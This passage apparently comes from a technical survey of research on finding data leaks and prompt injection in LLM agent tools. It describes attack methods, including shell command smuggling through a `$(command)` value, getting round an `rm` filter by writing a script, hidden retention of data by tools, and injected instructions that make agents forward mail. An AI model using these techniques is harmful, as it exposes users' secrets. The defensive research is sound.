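In *SkillsMetric*, Chen, Ji and colleagues (2026) measured which attacks a static scanner can detect. Their scanner scores each skill on text patterns, unusual byte statistics, data flow, unusual software imports, and mismatches between what a skill declares and what it does. It flags a skill at 25 points. A complete data flow, such as code that reads a password, encodes it and sends it out, scores 30 points, enough to trigger a flag by itself. Each of the other four categories can add at most 20 points.

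The team tested the scanner on 2,000 ordinary skills and 266 malicious ones that they had made, mostly by adding attacks to real skills. These are three of the 16 attack types:

| Attack | Detected |
|---|---|
| Data exfiltration | 26 of 28 (93%) |
| Prompt injection in the instructions | 5 of 12 (42%) |
| Destroying files on the user's machine | 0 of 11 (0%) |

Code that steals data has to move it from a source to a sink, and that path is visible in the code. But deleting a user's projects takes only one call to `shutil.rmtree`, which cleanup scripts also use. An injected instruction may contain no code at all, and the scanner caught five only because they included code blocks that matched its patterns.

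Chen and colleagues scored the instruction files of 138,133 real skills, and most of the highest scores went to legitimate security tools, such as virus scanners and programs for testing a company's defences.

### Malicious skills and careless ones

Much of the disagreement between these results comes from whether the skills tested were malicious, meaning written to do harm, or careless, meaning written honestly but with a flaw that someone else can exploit. Li, Guo and colleagues (2026) argue in *Carried-Over and Agent-Native Threats in the Supply Chain of LLM Agent Skills* that detecting malicious skills requires evidence of harmful behaviour, while detecting careless ones calls for taint analysis and a check for outdated software that the skill depends on.

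A known attack command in a malicious skill may be enough to justify flagging it, and following the data adds little. The attack may also be outside the skill. Of 703 malicious skills collected from ClawHub for *MalSkillBench* (2026), 607 included instructions for the user or agent to install a fake prerequisite first. A taint tracker that examines only the skill can't follow data through a program that hasn't been downloaded yet.

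A careless skill may contain no suspicious command. Gandhi and colleagues found no sign of malice in any of the skills with confirmed flaws. One of them, from the popular Streamlit project, tells the agent to treat a GitHub issue as the specification for a new feature and to work without pausing for approval. These instructions are reasonable only if the issue comes from someone trusted. Most of the confirmed flaws came from instructions like these, which explains why a language model found more of the flaws than value tracking did.

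Even if a carelessly written skill has a confirmed flow, an attack might not use it. Li, Guo and colleagues checked all 48,682 skills on ClawHub and confirmed 315 in which an agent's input could reach a command or run as code. They then attacked a live agent through planted content, using 200 skills their scanner had flagged. The attacker's command ran in 48.5% of cases but reached a flaw in the skill itself in only 5.0%.

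In nearly all the other successful attacks, the agent's own shell ran the command before the skill started. For example, a travel skill may tell the agent to run a script with a city name. If a web page gives the city as `$(command)`, the shell runs that command while preparing the script's arguments. The attack would work even if the script were flawless, so an analysis of the script alone would miss it.

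The same team looked for skills that print passwords or keys, which puts those secrets in the model's context. They confirmed 22 real leaks. Only 5.1% of the results flagged by their taint-tracking search were correct, because many scripts printed only a key's name or a masked version of the key.

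## Deriving each tool's capabilities from its code: ACaM

In November 2026, Santra and colleagues at IBM and Pennsylvania State University described ACaM, which combines the two methods. It uses taint tracking on each tool's code to work out what the tool can do, puts the results into a graph of the whole agent, and searches the graph for leaks. Toxic flow analysis, by contrast, labels tools largely by their descriptions.

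### How often descriptions and code disagree

The 10% mismatch rate mentioned earlier is a share of tools and the 13% rate is a share of servers, so they don't estimate the same thing.

The 10% comes from *Description-Code Inconsistency in Real-world MCP Servers* (Shi, Zhang and colleagues, 2026). The researchers had a language model compare the descriptions of Python tools with their code. The wording of a question tends to sway a model's answer, so they asked about each tool twice, once whether the description and code matched and once whether they conflicted. If the answers contradicted each other, a third prompt decided. Of 19,200 tools, 1,907 had a mismatch, which is 9.9% of all the tools, or 11.2% of the 17,030 with a usable description.

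The true rate may be higher. To test the detector, the researchers checked 200 tools it had called inconsistent and 200 it had called consistent. They found eight errors in the first group and five in the second, which gives a recall of 97.5% on the sample. But the detector called about eight times as many tools consistent as inconsistent, so a sample with equal numbers of each underrepresents its misses. If 2.5% of all the tools it called consistent had a mismatch, as in the sample, it missed about 380, its recall was about 83%, and the true rate was about 13%. This estimate is uncertain because it is based on only five errors.

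Many of the mismatches had nothing to do with theft. The most common problem, found in 35% of them, was that the description promised features the code lacked. Undeclared side effects, which include data leaks, hidden changes and heavy use of resources, made up 24.8% of the mismatches and affected about 2.8% of the tools with usable descriptions. One tool that supposedly echoed a message also returned the server's `SECRET_KEY`. Another, for converting "local" PDF files, uploaded them to an outside service.

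Scanners can easily miss such leaks. Shi and colleagues made 40 test tools with undeclared data leaks. Snyk's Agent Scan raised an alert of at least medium severity for only five of them, while Bandit flagged 31.

The 13% comes from Li, Ma and colleagues (2026), in *Don't believe everything you read*. They compared the README files and similar documents of 10,240 servers with what the code did, and found that 1,393 servers left a substantial share of their functions undocumented. One was a stock-trading server whose documentation didn't mention that it could place and cancel orders. The researchers deliberately ignored documented features that the code didn't implement. At the tool level, 35% of servers had at least one mismatch.

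A description can also state a tool's purpose accurately but understate what the tool can access. In *My Credentials, Please*, Huang, Tang and colleagues (2026) call this capability laundering when an attacker can make the tool access files outside its proper scope. For example, the `git_add` tool in Anthropic's Git server accepted paths outside the project, so an agent could stage a private file and then read its contents through a later call that displayed the staged changes. The researchers confirmed 150 flaws by running the tools, mostly by placing fake credentials outside the permitted scope and checking whether the tools returned them. Santra and colleagues use the term more broadly, for any dangerous capability that no tool's description declares.

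### A token that leaves through shared state

Santra and colleagues explain ACaM with an agent that has two tools. This is a slightly shortened version:

```python
STATE = {"lang": "en"}

def get_news(topic):
    token = os.environ["NEWS_API_TOKEN"]
    STATE["token"] = token
    reply = requests.get(NEWS_URL, params={"q": topic, "key": token})
    return reply.text

def sync_prefs():
    requests.post(PREFS_URL, json=STATE)
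    return "synced"
```

`get_news` sends the token to the news service that requires it, and `sync_prefs` sends the user's settings to the service that stores them. Each tool looks reasonable alone, but after `get_news` has run, the settings include the token, so the next call to `sync_prefs` sends it to a service that doesn't need it. Nobody has to plant an instruction for this to happen, and the token never enters the context of the agent's model.

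Neither single-function nor cross-function analysis finds the leak, because `sync_prefs` reads no credential itself and neither function calls the other.

ACaM first divides the program into components and conduits. A component is a piece of code, such as a tool. A conduit is a channel that data passes through, such as a file, a web request or a shared variable. Each conduit gets a starting label, which Santra and colleagues call a seed:

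| Conduit | Seed | Reason |
|---|---|---|
| `NEWS_API_TOKEN` | secret | the name suggests a credential |
| `STATE` | internal | default for shared variables |
| request to the news service | public | outsiders can reach network data |
| post to the preferences service | public | outsiders can reach network data |

ACaM then tracks taint inside each component, much as in the trace of `forward_ticket`, but it gives each field a separate label and also follows implicit flows. It analyses the tools that write to a conduit before the tools that read from it. When `get_news` stores the token, ACaM promotes that field of `STATE` from internal to secret and records which tool wrote it. So when it analyses `sync_prefs`, it finds that the tool reads a secret.

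This order exists only if no two tools each read what the other writes. By default, ACaM leaves any such pair out of its schedule. None of the agents that Santra and colleagues tested had this problem, but an agent with two tools that both read and update a shared notebook would.

### Answers that depend on another tool

Next, ACaM checks each component against a list of questions. Nineteen are fixed, such as whether the component reads secrets, writes files or runs generated code. A language model adds others to suit the particular agent, in this case whether the tools relay a secret through shared state.

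Some answers depend on another tool, so ACaM first records them as conditions:

| Question | First answer | Final answer |
|---|---|---|
| Does `get_news` read a secret? | yes | yes |
| Does `get_news` leak a secret itself? | no | no |
| Is `get_news` part of a relay? | only if `sync_prefs` leaks a secret | yes |
| Does `sync_prefs` read a secret? | only if `get_news` writes one to `STATE` | yes |
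| Does `sync_prefs` leak a secret? | only if `get_news` writes one to `STATE` | yes |
| Is `sync_prefs` part of a relay? | only if `get_news` writes one to `STATE` | yes |

ACaM settles the conditions in rounds. In the first round, it finds that `get_news` writes a secret to `STATE`, so all three answers about `sync_prefs` become yes. That satisfies the condition on `get_news`, so its answer also becomes yes in the same round. The next round changes nothing, so ACaM stops. The rounds always end because a yes or no answer never changes. If a condition is still open at the end, ACaM records the answer as unknown rather than no.

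Finally, ACaM searches the graph for nine kinds of dangerous path, without using a language model. It finds the leak, which is a path from `NEWS_API_TOKEN` through `get_news`, `STATE` and `sync_prefs` to the preferences service. The programmer can break this path by keeping the token out of `STATE`.

### Untrusted text on its own track

ACaM tracks secrets and untrusted data separately. In the example, the token is on the secret track and the news text is on the untrusted track.

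`get_news` returns the text to the agent's model, so an attacker who can influence the news could plant a prompt injection in it. `sync_prefs` also receives a reply from the internet, but discards it and returns a fixed word. ACaM marks a tool as an injection risk only if it lies on a complete path from outside data to the model, so it should mark `get_news` but not `sync_prefs`.

ACaM assumes that untrusted text, once it reaches the model, can influence any tool the model can call, as in the graph of the GitHub attack. But it counts a secret as reaching the model only if a tool returns it, so the news token doesn't spread through the model to every other tool.

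### What the language model may decide

ACaM uses a language model because some questions depend on what code means, and no fixed list of rules could cover every such case. For example, a program that branches on `user.role` is probably checking the user's privileges, while a branch on `user.lang` has the same structure but only chooses a language.

The model can't override facts established by static analysis. If the analysis finds that the code reads a secret, the model can't change that answer to no, and ACaM recomputes the fixed answers after each reply in case the model altered one. The model may raise a conduit's seed but not lower it. Santra and colleagues give static analysis priority because models lose intermediate steps in long chains and tend to accept a tool's description as true, which a dishonest author would falsify.

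This rule protects facts about where data goes, but the model still judges whether the recipient should have it. In the example, the model decides that `get_news` doesn't leak the token, because the news service needs it to identify the user. This judgment avoids a false alarm that a rule against sending any secret would raise. But a hostile tool author could exploit it by sending stolen credentials to an address named `AUTH_URL`, which might persuade the model that the request was a login.

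### Tests with known answers

Santra and colleagues tested ACaM's output on 24 agents they had annotated by hand. Ten were real agents from GitHub. The other 14 were copies of those ten in which the researchers had planted leaks without changing the tools' descriptions.

They measured accuracy with the F1 score, which is high only if precision and recall are both high:

F1 = 2 × precision × recall / (precision + recall)

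The macro-F1 score averages the F1 scores for each possible answer, so rare answers count as much as common ones. ACaM scored 98.3%. Its static analysis alone scored 93.4%, and language models alone scored 81.4%, even though the researchers chose the best of 12 combinations of model and prompt for each agent.

Static analysis therefore accounts for most of the score. On the 14 agents with planted leaks, adding the model raised the average from 92.3% to 99.3%, but two agents account for most of that gain. Without them, the averages are 98.3% and 99.4%. The model seems to help only a few agents much, including one whose score rose from 42.8% to 98.3%.

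Another test used the 14 altered agents to measure how well ACaM could reconstruct a whole leak. Each leak had seven facts to recover, including the secret's name, the function that reads it, the order of the calls and the place where the data leaves. A correct fact earned one point and a partly correct one earned half a point, and the score was the total divided by seven. ACaM averaged 0.980, compared with 0.903 for Claude Sonnet 4.6 alone and 0.888 for Claude Opus 4.8.

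The static analysers did far worse. Pysa, Meta's taint tracker for Python, scored 0.342, and Semgrep scored 0.265. When the researchers told Pysa to assume that taint passes straight through the agent's model, its score fell to 0.225. Grouping the published scores by type of leak shows where these programs fail:

| Planted leak | Agents | ACaM | Sonnet 4.6 | Pysa | Semgrep |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
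| A tool returns the secret to the model | 8 | 0.96 | 0.88 | 0.25 | 0.06 |
| A tool posts the secret itself | 3 | 1.00 | 0.95 | 0.93 | 0.83 |
| Mixed, including shared state or a second program | 3 | 1.00 | 0.91 | 0.00 | 0.24 |

Pysa and Semgrep did well at detecting leaks inside one tool's code, but mostly failed when the secret had to pass through the model or a shared channel.

The gap between ACaM and Sonnet is smaller than it may look, since Sonnet's score of 0.903 means it lost about two thirds of a point per leak. Most of the difference came from the full chain of calls, which the models got wrong or incomplete 40% of the time, compared with 7% for ACaM. A programmer who knows the secret and the exit can often find the steps between them by hand.

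The researchers planted all these leaks themselves. They based the leaks on published attacks, but they knew which channels ACaM could follow. A test with leaks planted by another team would be more convincing.

### Paths in 43 real agents

Santra and colleagues then ran ACaM on 43 unmodified agents from GitHub, including the ten above. The 43 agents averaged about six tools each. ACaM reported 123 critical paths, and the researchers checked by hand that each one existed in the code. In 107 of them, an attacker could run code, and in 16, a credential could reach an outside service.

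ACaM also reported about 1,800 less severe paths, which only a separate language-model agent checked. The agent accepted 99.4% of the high-severity candidates and 98.4% of the medium-severity ones, which implies false-positive rates of 0.6% and 1.6%, but only if its judgments were correct. The agent ran on Sonnet 4.6, which ACaM also uses to fill gaps in its answers, so the two could easily make the same mistakes. The agent also read the source files directly, so a hostile author could mislead it with comments in the code. A human audit of a sample, like the one of SkillReact's matches, would give a better estimate.

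Two agents produced 85% of the rejected candidates. The largest source of false alarms was internal files that ACaM treated as possible carriers of prompt injection, although an outside attacker usually can't write to them.

Of the 1,800 paths, 1,692 were for indirect prompt injection, an average of 39 per agent. Almost any agent that reads outside content will have some of these paths. Santra and colleagues count each combination of source and sink separately because closing one path can leave another open, but a developer can't do much with 39 warnings that outside text may reach the model.

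The best evidence is ten working attacks on nine of the agents. Six let the attacker run code, and in one of these the researchers also stole user records. Another attack returned other customers' records in two of four attempts. None of the ten came from the credential-exposure group, so a real leak like the one in `sync_prefs` has been found in code but not demonstrated in a running agent.

The researchers first ran the attacks with Qwen2.5-7B, a small model with little safety training. Claude Haiku 4.5 blocked the blunt versions, but all ten worked when the researchers phrased them more subtly. They didn't test larger Claude models, which might have resisted some of the attacks. At least two attacks don't depend on the model, because the agent runs the attacker's code while loading a doctored file at startup. Those attacks require write access to files on the same machine.

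### Costs and blind spots

An analysis costs about 77 cents per agent and takes just under a minute on average. The static part takes five seconds and incurs no model fees. Over 15 repeated runs, between 0.5% and 2% of the answers changed. Replacing Sonnet with the cheaper Haiku 4.5 lowered the macro-F1 score to 95.2%, still well above the scores of the language models on their own.

ACaM needs the source code, so it can't examine a tool on someone else's server, and it can analyse only Python. Santra and colleagues don't consider developers who disguise their code to evade analysis. ACaM marks code it can't resolve as unknown, so a user would at least find out that part of the agent was unchecked.

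When a tool builds a file path while running, ACaM can't tell whether the file holds credentials, so it labels the contents internal. It would therefore miss some real leaks, but labelling every such file secret would cause too many false alarms.

ACaM also never lowers a label because of a sanitiser. It would keep the host in `forward_ticket` labelled untrusted even after the programmer added a correct allow-list. This avoids Agent Audit's mistake of hiding a real flaw because of a useless type check, but it can produce warnings about code that is already safe.

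### Chains that people reproduced

SCAN-MCP, which also builds a graph from the code of an agent's tools, has had a stricter test on real software. In *Agent Smith in Action*, analysts tried to reproduce all 150 reports that SCAN-MCP produced for a sample of 100 MCP servers. They confirmed 105 of the 130 reports about single tools and 19 of the 20 about chains of tools.

They then tried each of the 19 confirmed chains again with only the last tool, and none of the attacks worked. In one kind of chain, a tool that runs commands refuses any command containing `rm`, which deletes files. The attacker uses another tool to write a script containing `rm`, then runs the script with the command tool. A reviewer who tested the command tool alone would find that its check worked.

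SCAN-MCP's filters help it reach 83% precision, but they also remove real problems. When the researchers switched the filters off, the number of reports rose from 150 to 519, and the analysts confirmed 44 more problems. The filtered version had therefore found 124 of the 168 problems confirmed in this test, or 74%. SCAN-MCP also considers only tools on the same server, while ACaM covers a whole agent.

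### An analyser that also repairs the code

In *Data Leakage Prevention in Agentic Applications via Preemptive Hardening*, Shukla, Bellov and colleagues (2026) give the language model a larger role. Their program parses Python code to find an agent's tools and marks every tool that makes outbound requests as a possible exit for data. It also rates each argument by how much data it could carry, since a free-form string can hold a secret more easily than a fixed choice. The language model then labels the sensitive data and lists the paths from it to the exits.

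For the news agent, this analyser would mark both tools as exits. The language model would then have to detect that the token passes through `STATE`, and models often missed this kind of intermediate step in ACaM's tests.

The program then repairs what it finds, for instance by restricting a tool's destinations, and attacks the repaired agent to check the result. The researchers tested it on five applications. After the repairs, none of the attacks worked on four, and at most 7.4% worked on the fifth, a network monitor. Without the analyser, the program applied every kind of repair everywhere, and attack success rose to between 17.6% and 36.8%. But Shukla and colleagues didn't compare the analyser's paths with a list of known leaks, so its precision and recall are unknown. The repairs also broke some legitimate work. A personnel assistant completed every ordinary task before the repairs,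 but only 76.9% afterwards.

### Watching what a tool does

Running a tool can also reveal its capabilities. *Auditing MCP Servers for Over-Privileged Tool Capabilities* (Huang, Huang and Milani Fard, 2026) describes mcp-sec-audit, which searches the text of Python code and tool descriptions for signs of capabilities such as writing files or running commands. It also includes a runtime check, in which the auditor starts the server in a sandbox, sends hostile inputs to its tools and records the files, programs and network connections they use.

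On nine deliberately vulnerable servers, the text search flagged both of the Python servers and none of the seven written in JavaScript, which it can't read. Runtime monitoring flagged all nine, but the test included no harmless servers, so it can't measure the monitoring's false alarm rate. Five of the JavaScript servers got the same risk score, 60.7, despite flaws as different as a misleading name and outdated packages, so the monitor may have been scoring something that any JavaScript server does in the sandbox.

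Runtime monitoring works for any programming language and doesn't rely on descriptions, but the order of the test calls can change the result. If the auditor ran `sync_prefs` before `get_news`, it would record a harmless post containing one language setting. In the opposite order, the post would contain the token, but a monitor that recorded only the connection would not record the token.

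## Following labels while the agent runs

A flag such as TF001 means that an agent could leak data. To find out whether private data is leaking in a particular run, a program has to label what each tool returns and track those labels as the agent works. In ordinary code, the analyser can follow a value from line to line. This is harder with a language model, which may turn a payroll file into the sentence "two directors earn more than everyone else combined", which shares almost no words with the file. The model may also call a different tool because of something it read on a stranger's web page, without copying any of the page's text.

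A tracker can assume that everything the model has read affects everything it writes, or it can look for evidence of what affected each call. The first approach blocks harmless requests, and the second can miss leaks.

### One label for the whole context

*Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf et al., 2025) describes FIDES, a Microsoft system that starts from the first approach. Like the graph of the GitHub attack, FIDES applies the worst-case rule to the model, but it joins only the labels of outputs the agent has received in this run. The program around the model keeps the labels, so an injection can't make the model change them.

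The confidentiality label can be a list of people who may read the data. If Ann and Ben may read one file, and Ben and Carol may read another, only Ben may read a text based on both. The join of two labels is therefore the intersection of their lists.

FIDES checks the labels before it carries out a call. In the version that Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues (2026) describe in *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy*, a tool may send data if at least one of two conditions holds:

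- The context is trusted, which means that the model has read nothing an outsider could have written.
- Every recipient may read the data.

Suppose a user tells the office assistant, "Summarise the new reviews, check that the payroll adds up, and confirm Friday's lunch with the caterer." The assistant makes three calls:

| Call | Label of the output | Label of the context afterwards |
|---|---|---|
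| `read_reviews` | untrusted, public | untrusted, public |
| `read_payroll` | trusted, secret | untrusted, secret |
| `send_email` to the caterer | – | the system blocks the call |

Neither condition holds, because the context is untrusted and the caterer is not allowed to read the payroll. This is true even though the email contains only "Friday's lunch is confirmed" and none of the reviews contains an injection. If the assistant had sent the email first, the system would have allowed it.

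### Hiding text from the model that plans

FIDES avoids many of these blocks by keeping some tool results away from the planning model, which chooses the tool calls. If a result would raise the context's label, FIDES stores it in a variable and shows the planning model only the variable's name. A second, quarantined model, which has no tools, can read the contents and put a summary in another variable. In the lunch example, the quarantined model could summarise the reviews and check the payroll. The planning model could then send the email because its context would still be trusted.

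Google DeepMind's CaMeL also separates a planning model from a quarantined one, as Willison proposed in 2023. *CaMeLoT* (2026), which extends CaMeL, describes CaMeL's policies as Python functions that inspect a tool call and its arguments, then allow or deny the call and give a reason. Without these policies, the separation isn't enough to stop attacks. When *The LLMbda Calculus* (2026) reran CaMeL with the policies switched off, 138 of 141 attacks in one category succeeded with the model MiMo-v2.5. With the policies on, CaMeL blocked every attack but completed far fewer tasks.

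Some requests depend on the content of the hidden text. If the user says, "Check my email and book a meeting if anyone asks for one," the planning model has to learn whether anyone did. Kolluri and colleagues explain that a CaMeL plan can't depend on tool results, whereas FIDES lets the planning model open a variable, which taints the model's context. FIDES can also restrict the quarantined model to answering yes or no, so its answer can't contain an instruction.

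Costa and colleagues tested these designs on AgentDojo, a benchmark of simulated office, travel, banking and Slack tasks. With GPT-4o, 152 attacks succeeded against an agent without checks, and none succeeded once the policies were on. The table shows the share of ordinary tasks that the agents completed when not under attack.

| Tasks | No checks | One label for the context | FIDES |
|---|---|---|---|
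| Office | 75.0% | 37.0% | 59.0% |
| Travel | 70.0% | 73.0% | 41.0% |
| Banking | 98.8% | 37.5% | 52.5% |
| Slack | 93.3% | 20.0% | 47.6% |

The simple rule does little harm to the travel tasks because the policy lets many travel tools run in an untrusted context. FIDES does worse on them because GPT-4o handled the variables poorly. With o1, a stronger reasoning model, FIDES completed 68% of the travel tasks. Some of the banking failures are intentional, since those tasks require the agent to follow instructions in a file that an outsider could have changed.

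A narrower policy can let an agent complete more tasks. *Formal Policy Enforcement for Agentic Systems* (2026) compared the FIDES policy with one based on where data came from. On AgentDojo, the agent completed 33.2% of ordinary tasks under the FIDES policy and 62.5% under the origin-based policy.

A blocked call also doesn't have to end the task, because the system can ask the user to approve it. Kolluri and colleagues argue that the fair comparison is with agents that ask before every consequential action. With the model o3-mini, such an agent completed 24.3% of AgentDojo tasks without needing to ask. Using one label for the whole context raised this to 35.5%, and FIDES raised it to 50.1%. Prudentia, their version of FIDES, reached 59.1% by telling the planning model about the labels and policies so it could plan around them.

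Prudentia can also ask the user to endorse a piece of untrusted text. If an email lists ten tasks, the user can approve the email once instead of approving ten separate calls. But if the user overlooks an injection in the email, they approve the injection too.

### Finding the source of a rewritten text

*Ghost in the Agent* (Cai, Wen and colleagues, 2026) takes the second approach with a program called NeuroTaint. It records an agent's run and afterwards looks for links between sources, such as a web search, and sinks, such as sending an email. The developer chooses which tools count as sources and sinks, so a file reader can be a source too. NeuroTaint also saves labels with the agent's stored notes, so it could connect the report sent on Tuesday in the earlier example with the web page the agent read on Monday.

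For each call to a sink, NeuroTaint compares the call's arguments with every source that could have reached it. It makes up to four comparisons, starting with the cheapest:

1. During the run, it adds a random code to the source's output. It then checks whether the code appears in the arguments.
2. It measures how much of the shorter text also occurs in the longer one in the same order. An overlap of 15% is normally enough.
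3. It converts both texts into embeddings, which are lists of numbers that represent meaning, and measures their similarity. The usual threshold is 0.60, where 1 is the highest possible score.
4. It compares the arguments with a few sentences of the source at a time, because one planted sentence hardly changes the meaning of a long page.

For example, a page may tell the agent to forward all emails to an archive address. The agent may later write that it is good practice to copy in the archiving service. The wording has changed too much for the second comparison to find a match, but the third can still match the meaning.

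### Finding what swayed a decision

If all four comparisons fail, NeuroTaint checks whether the source influenced the agent's decision, which would be similar to an implicit flow in ordinary code. It replaces the source's output with neutral text such as "No relevant information found" and asks a language model whether the agent would still have made the same call. If not, NeuroTaint reports a link. When several sources could be responsible, it replaces them one at a time.

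In one test case, an agent searches the web and normally runs some code on the results. A planted search result claims that the agent must first submit everything to an outside server, so the agent posts its research there. The posted text comes from the research, not the planted result, but the server's address appears in both the planted result the agent read and the request it sent, so comparing the texts might still catch this case. An attack would be harder to detect if a page persuaded the agent to send the research to someone already in the user's address book.

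The published prompt has the model predict what the agent would have done, so a wrong prediction can result in a missed link or a false one. The model also outputs an estimate of its own confidence, which Cai and colleagues warn is not a calibrated probability.

A correct prediction doesn't prove that anything bad happened, either. If a user asks the agent to accept any emailed invitation for a free evening, the agent replies only because an invitation arrived. NeuroTaint would rightly report that the email influenced the reply, but the user would still have to decide whether that was harmful.

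### NeuroTaint's results on TaintBench

Cai and colleagues built TaintBench, a benchmark of 400 scenarios in 20 agent frameworks. In half of the scenarios, something from a source reaches or influences a sink. The agents ran on GPT-4.1-mini. The researchers used a baseline modelled on FIDES, which treats a path from a source to a sink as strong evidence of a flow. The table groups their published results.

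| Type of scenario | Number | Flagged by NeuroTaint | Flagged by the baseline |
|---|---|---|---|
| Copied text | 60 | 60 | 45 |
| A small part of a long text | 15 | 15 | 6 |
| Rewritten or delayed text | 85 | 75 | 40 |
| A swayed decision | 40 | 37 | 17 |
| No flow, but a similar topic | 14 | 14 | 9 |
| Other scenarios without a flow | 186 | 2 | 97 |

NeuroTaint had 92.1% precision and 93.5% recall, for an F1 score of 0.928. The baseline had 50.5% precision and 54.0% recall, for an F1 score of 0.522.

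NeuroTaint raised only 16 false alarms, but it was wrong in all 14 scenarios where the agent wrote about the same topic as the source without using the source. Such errors could be common in an office, where an agent often reads web pages and writes emails about the same project.

The baseline's low recall is weak evidence about the conservative rule. If the system labels a source correctly and joins every label, it can't miss a direct flow within one session. But the baseline flagged nothing in the 80 scenarios from four of the frameworks, which suggests it didn't work properly with them. On two older benchmarks that measure unsafe actions, the methods were almost equal. Both had an F1 score of 0.760 on ToolEmu, and on the basic version of InjecAgent they scored 0.994 and 0.993.

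A stronger agent makes the results harder to interpret. When Claude Opus 4.6 ran the agents, NeuroTaint's recall fell to 54.7%, partly because the model resisted attacks before they reached a sink, and those attacks count as misses.

NeuroTaint adds little overhead, averaging 0.25 seconds per run and about 457 tokens for each check of whether a decision was swayed. But it reports flows only after the run, when the agent may already have emailed the payroll to a stranger. If a developer moved the check to just before each send, any flow it missed would still leak data. NeuroTaint found no flow in 197 of the 400 scenarios, but 13 of those (6.6%) contained one.

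*GIF* (2026) instead proposes measuring, inside the model, how much each passage in the context affects the output. It slightly changes the passage's numerical representation and measures how much the output shifts. A passage that hardly affects the output then contributes little to the output's label.

### Leaks without an attacker

A user of the agent app Pokee asks it to email the payment date and amount from a transaction record to an auditor. The file reader returns the whole record, and the agent also sends the auditor the credit card number and its security code. Lin, Wu and colleagues (2026), in *AgentRaft*, use this case to introduce what they call data over-exposure. They define the over-exposed data as

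D_OE = (D_trans \ (D_nec ∪ D_int)) ∩ D_total

D_total is everything the source returned, D_trans is the part the agent sent, D_int is what the user meant to share, and D_nec is anything else the task required. The backslash removes the fields in D_nec and D_int, which in this case leaves the card number and security code.

AgentRaft tests an agent for such leaks before release. It works out which tools can supply data to which others, then writes requests that should make the agent use each path from a source to a sink. When it writes a request, AgentRaft chooses which fields the imaginary user intends to share, so it can label the other fields and look for them in what the agent sends, even in a different format. Three language models then vote on whether the task required each extra field.

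On four agents built for the test, AgentRaft reported 319 leaking paths, and human reviewers confirmed 295 of them, a precision of 92.48%. Lin and colleagues then tested five existing agent programs, including Claude Code, Codex and OpenClaw, with simulated data:

| What they counted | With over-exposure | Total | Share |
|---|---|---|---|
| Paths, with up to five requests each | 759 | 2,337 | 32.48% |
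| Individual requests | 2,896 | 11,009 | 26.31% |
| Fields sent in the leaking runs | 12,219 | 15,356 | 79.57% |

The share of requests that leaked ranged from 11.67% for Claude Code to 33.60% for Codex. All five programs used the same model, DeepSeek-V4-Flash, so the differences come from the programs themselves. The programs may behave differently with the models their users normally choose.

The lethal trifecta doesn't cover such accidents, and FIDES could miss them too. If the context is trusted, the first condition allows the email regardless of its contents, because Costa and colleagues assume that disclosures in a trusted context are intentional. AgentRaft's results show that this assumption often fails.

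Requiring permission to read the data as well would block the card number, but if one label covered the whole record, the date would be blocked too. The system needs a label for each field and has to keep the card number out of the planning model's context. FIDES can store fields in separate variables, so the planning model could pass on the date and amount without seeing the rest.

### Labels for a tool that lies

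FIDES and CaMeL assume that the tools are trustworthy. *Signed, Sealed, Leaked* (Aun, Alhartomi and colleagues, 2026) gives an example of one that isn't, a tool that extracts text from PDFs using an outside service, `ocr.example`. The service is allowed to receive financial documents but not personnel files. In an early call, the tool reads a salary sheet and secretly keeps a copy. When the agent later gives it an invoice, the tool adds the salary sheet to its request to the service.

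The labels describe the invoice correctly, and the tool is allowed to use the destination. The system fails because it assumes a call can send only the data it has just received. The news token in `STATE` leaked through the same kind of carry-over. A tool can also mix data within one call if the agent gives it both the invoice and the salary sheet.

Aun and colleagues' solution, germline execution, controls what the code can see, so nobody has to work out what it does. For each call, the system starts fresh copies of the tool from a process that has never held user data. In the second case, it makes two copies:

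- The first copy receives only the invoice and may contact `ocr.example`.
- The second copy receives both documents and returns its answer to the agent. The system never delivers its requests to `ocr.example`.

The system then discards both copies. If a tool needs to remember something, the system stores it with a label and gives it only to later copies that are allowed to see it.

The researchers wrote 51 attack cases and ran each three times under six kinds of protection.

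| Protection | Runs with a detected leak, of 153 |
|---|---|
| Signature check | 114 (74.5%) |
| Signature check and labels on replies | 108 (70.6%) |
| The same, with limits on files and destinations | 51 (33.3%) |
| The same, with a new process for each call | 15 (9.8%) |
| One fresh copy per call, holding all the data | 9 (5.9%) |
| Separate copies by destination | 0 |

A call that needed one copy took 10 to 49 milliseconds, and a call that needed three took 97. Aun and colleagues also made 780 calls to four official MCP servers without changing the servers' code. The results were the same as without the protection, except for clock times.

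They also found a gap in CaMeL's labels. A tool repeated a private email from an earlier call, but CaMeL labelled the new reply public and let it go to an untrusted recipient. The leak happened only because the test setup had declared that the tool had no side effects, a declaration CaMeL accepts without checking.

Germline execution needs correct labels and a list of destinations for each tool, and its guarantee doesn't cover timing channels. It also can't copy a tool that runs on someone else's server. It treats a whole host as one destination, so it probably wouldn't have stopped postmark-mcp, which sent its extra copies through an email service that was allowed to handle the message.

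### Which combination flags labels could lift

A label check can replace a flag only if it runs before the data leaves and covers every way out. This holds for the office assistant's 60 triples if its tools behave as described, the application labels all their outputs, and it checks every send. The owner could then keep all twelve tools and treat the flag as resolved for attacks through those tools. The Rule of Two could be relaxed in the same way, so that a session with all three properties needs approval only for calls that break a policy.

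Other flags are harder to lift:

| Flagged combination | What the labels would have to cover |
|---|---|
| `fetch_page` and `read_file` | The web addresses that the agent opens |
| An agent whose answers can load images, as in ForcedLeak | The final answer, which FIDES doesn't check by default |
| The backup and debugging skills | Files on disk, including the archive in the shared folder |
| A tool with untrusted code | Everything the tool has stored, with separate copies for destinations that may see different data |
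| `run_command` | Every program that the command starts |

The last flag should normally stay, because a single shell command can complete the whole theft before the system has another call to check.

NeuroTaint's results don't justify lifting any of these flags, because a clean log covers only one run and may be wrong. They could still help an owner decide which flag to deal with first. For example, if the logs repeatedly show strangers' text influencing emails, the owner could restrict `send_email` before looking at the other sinks.
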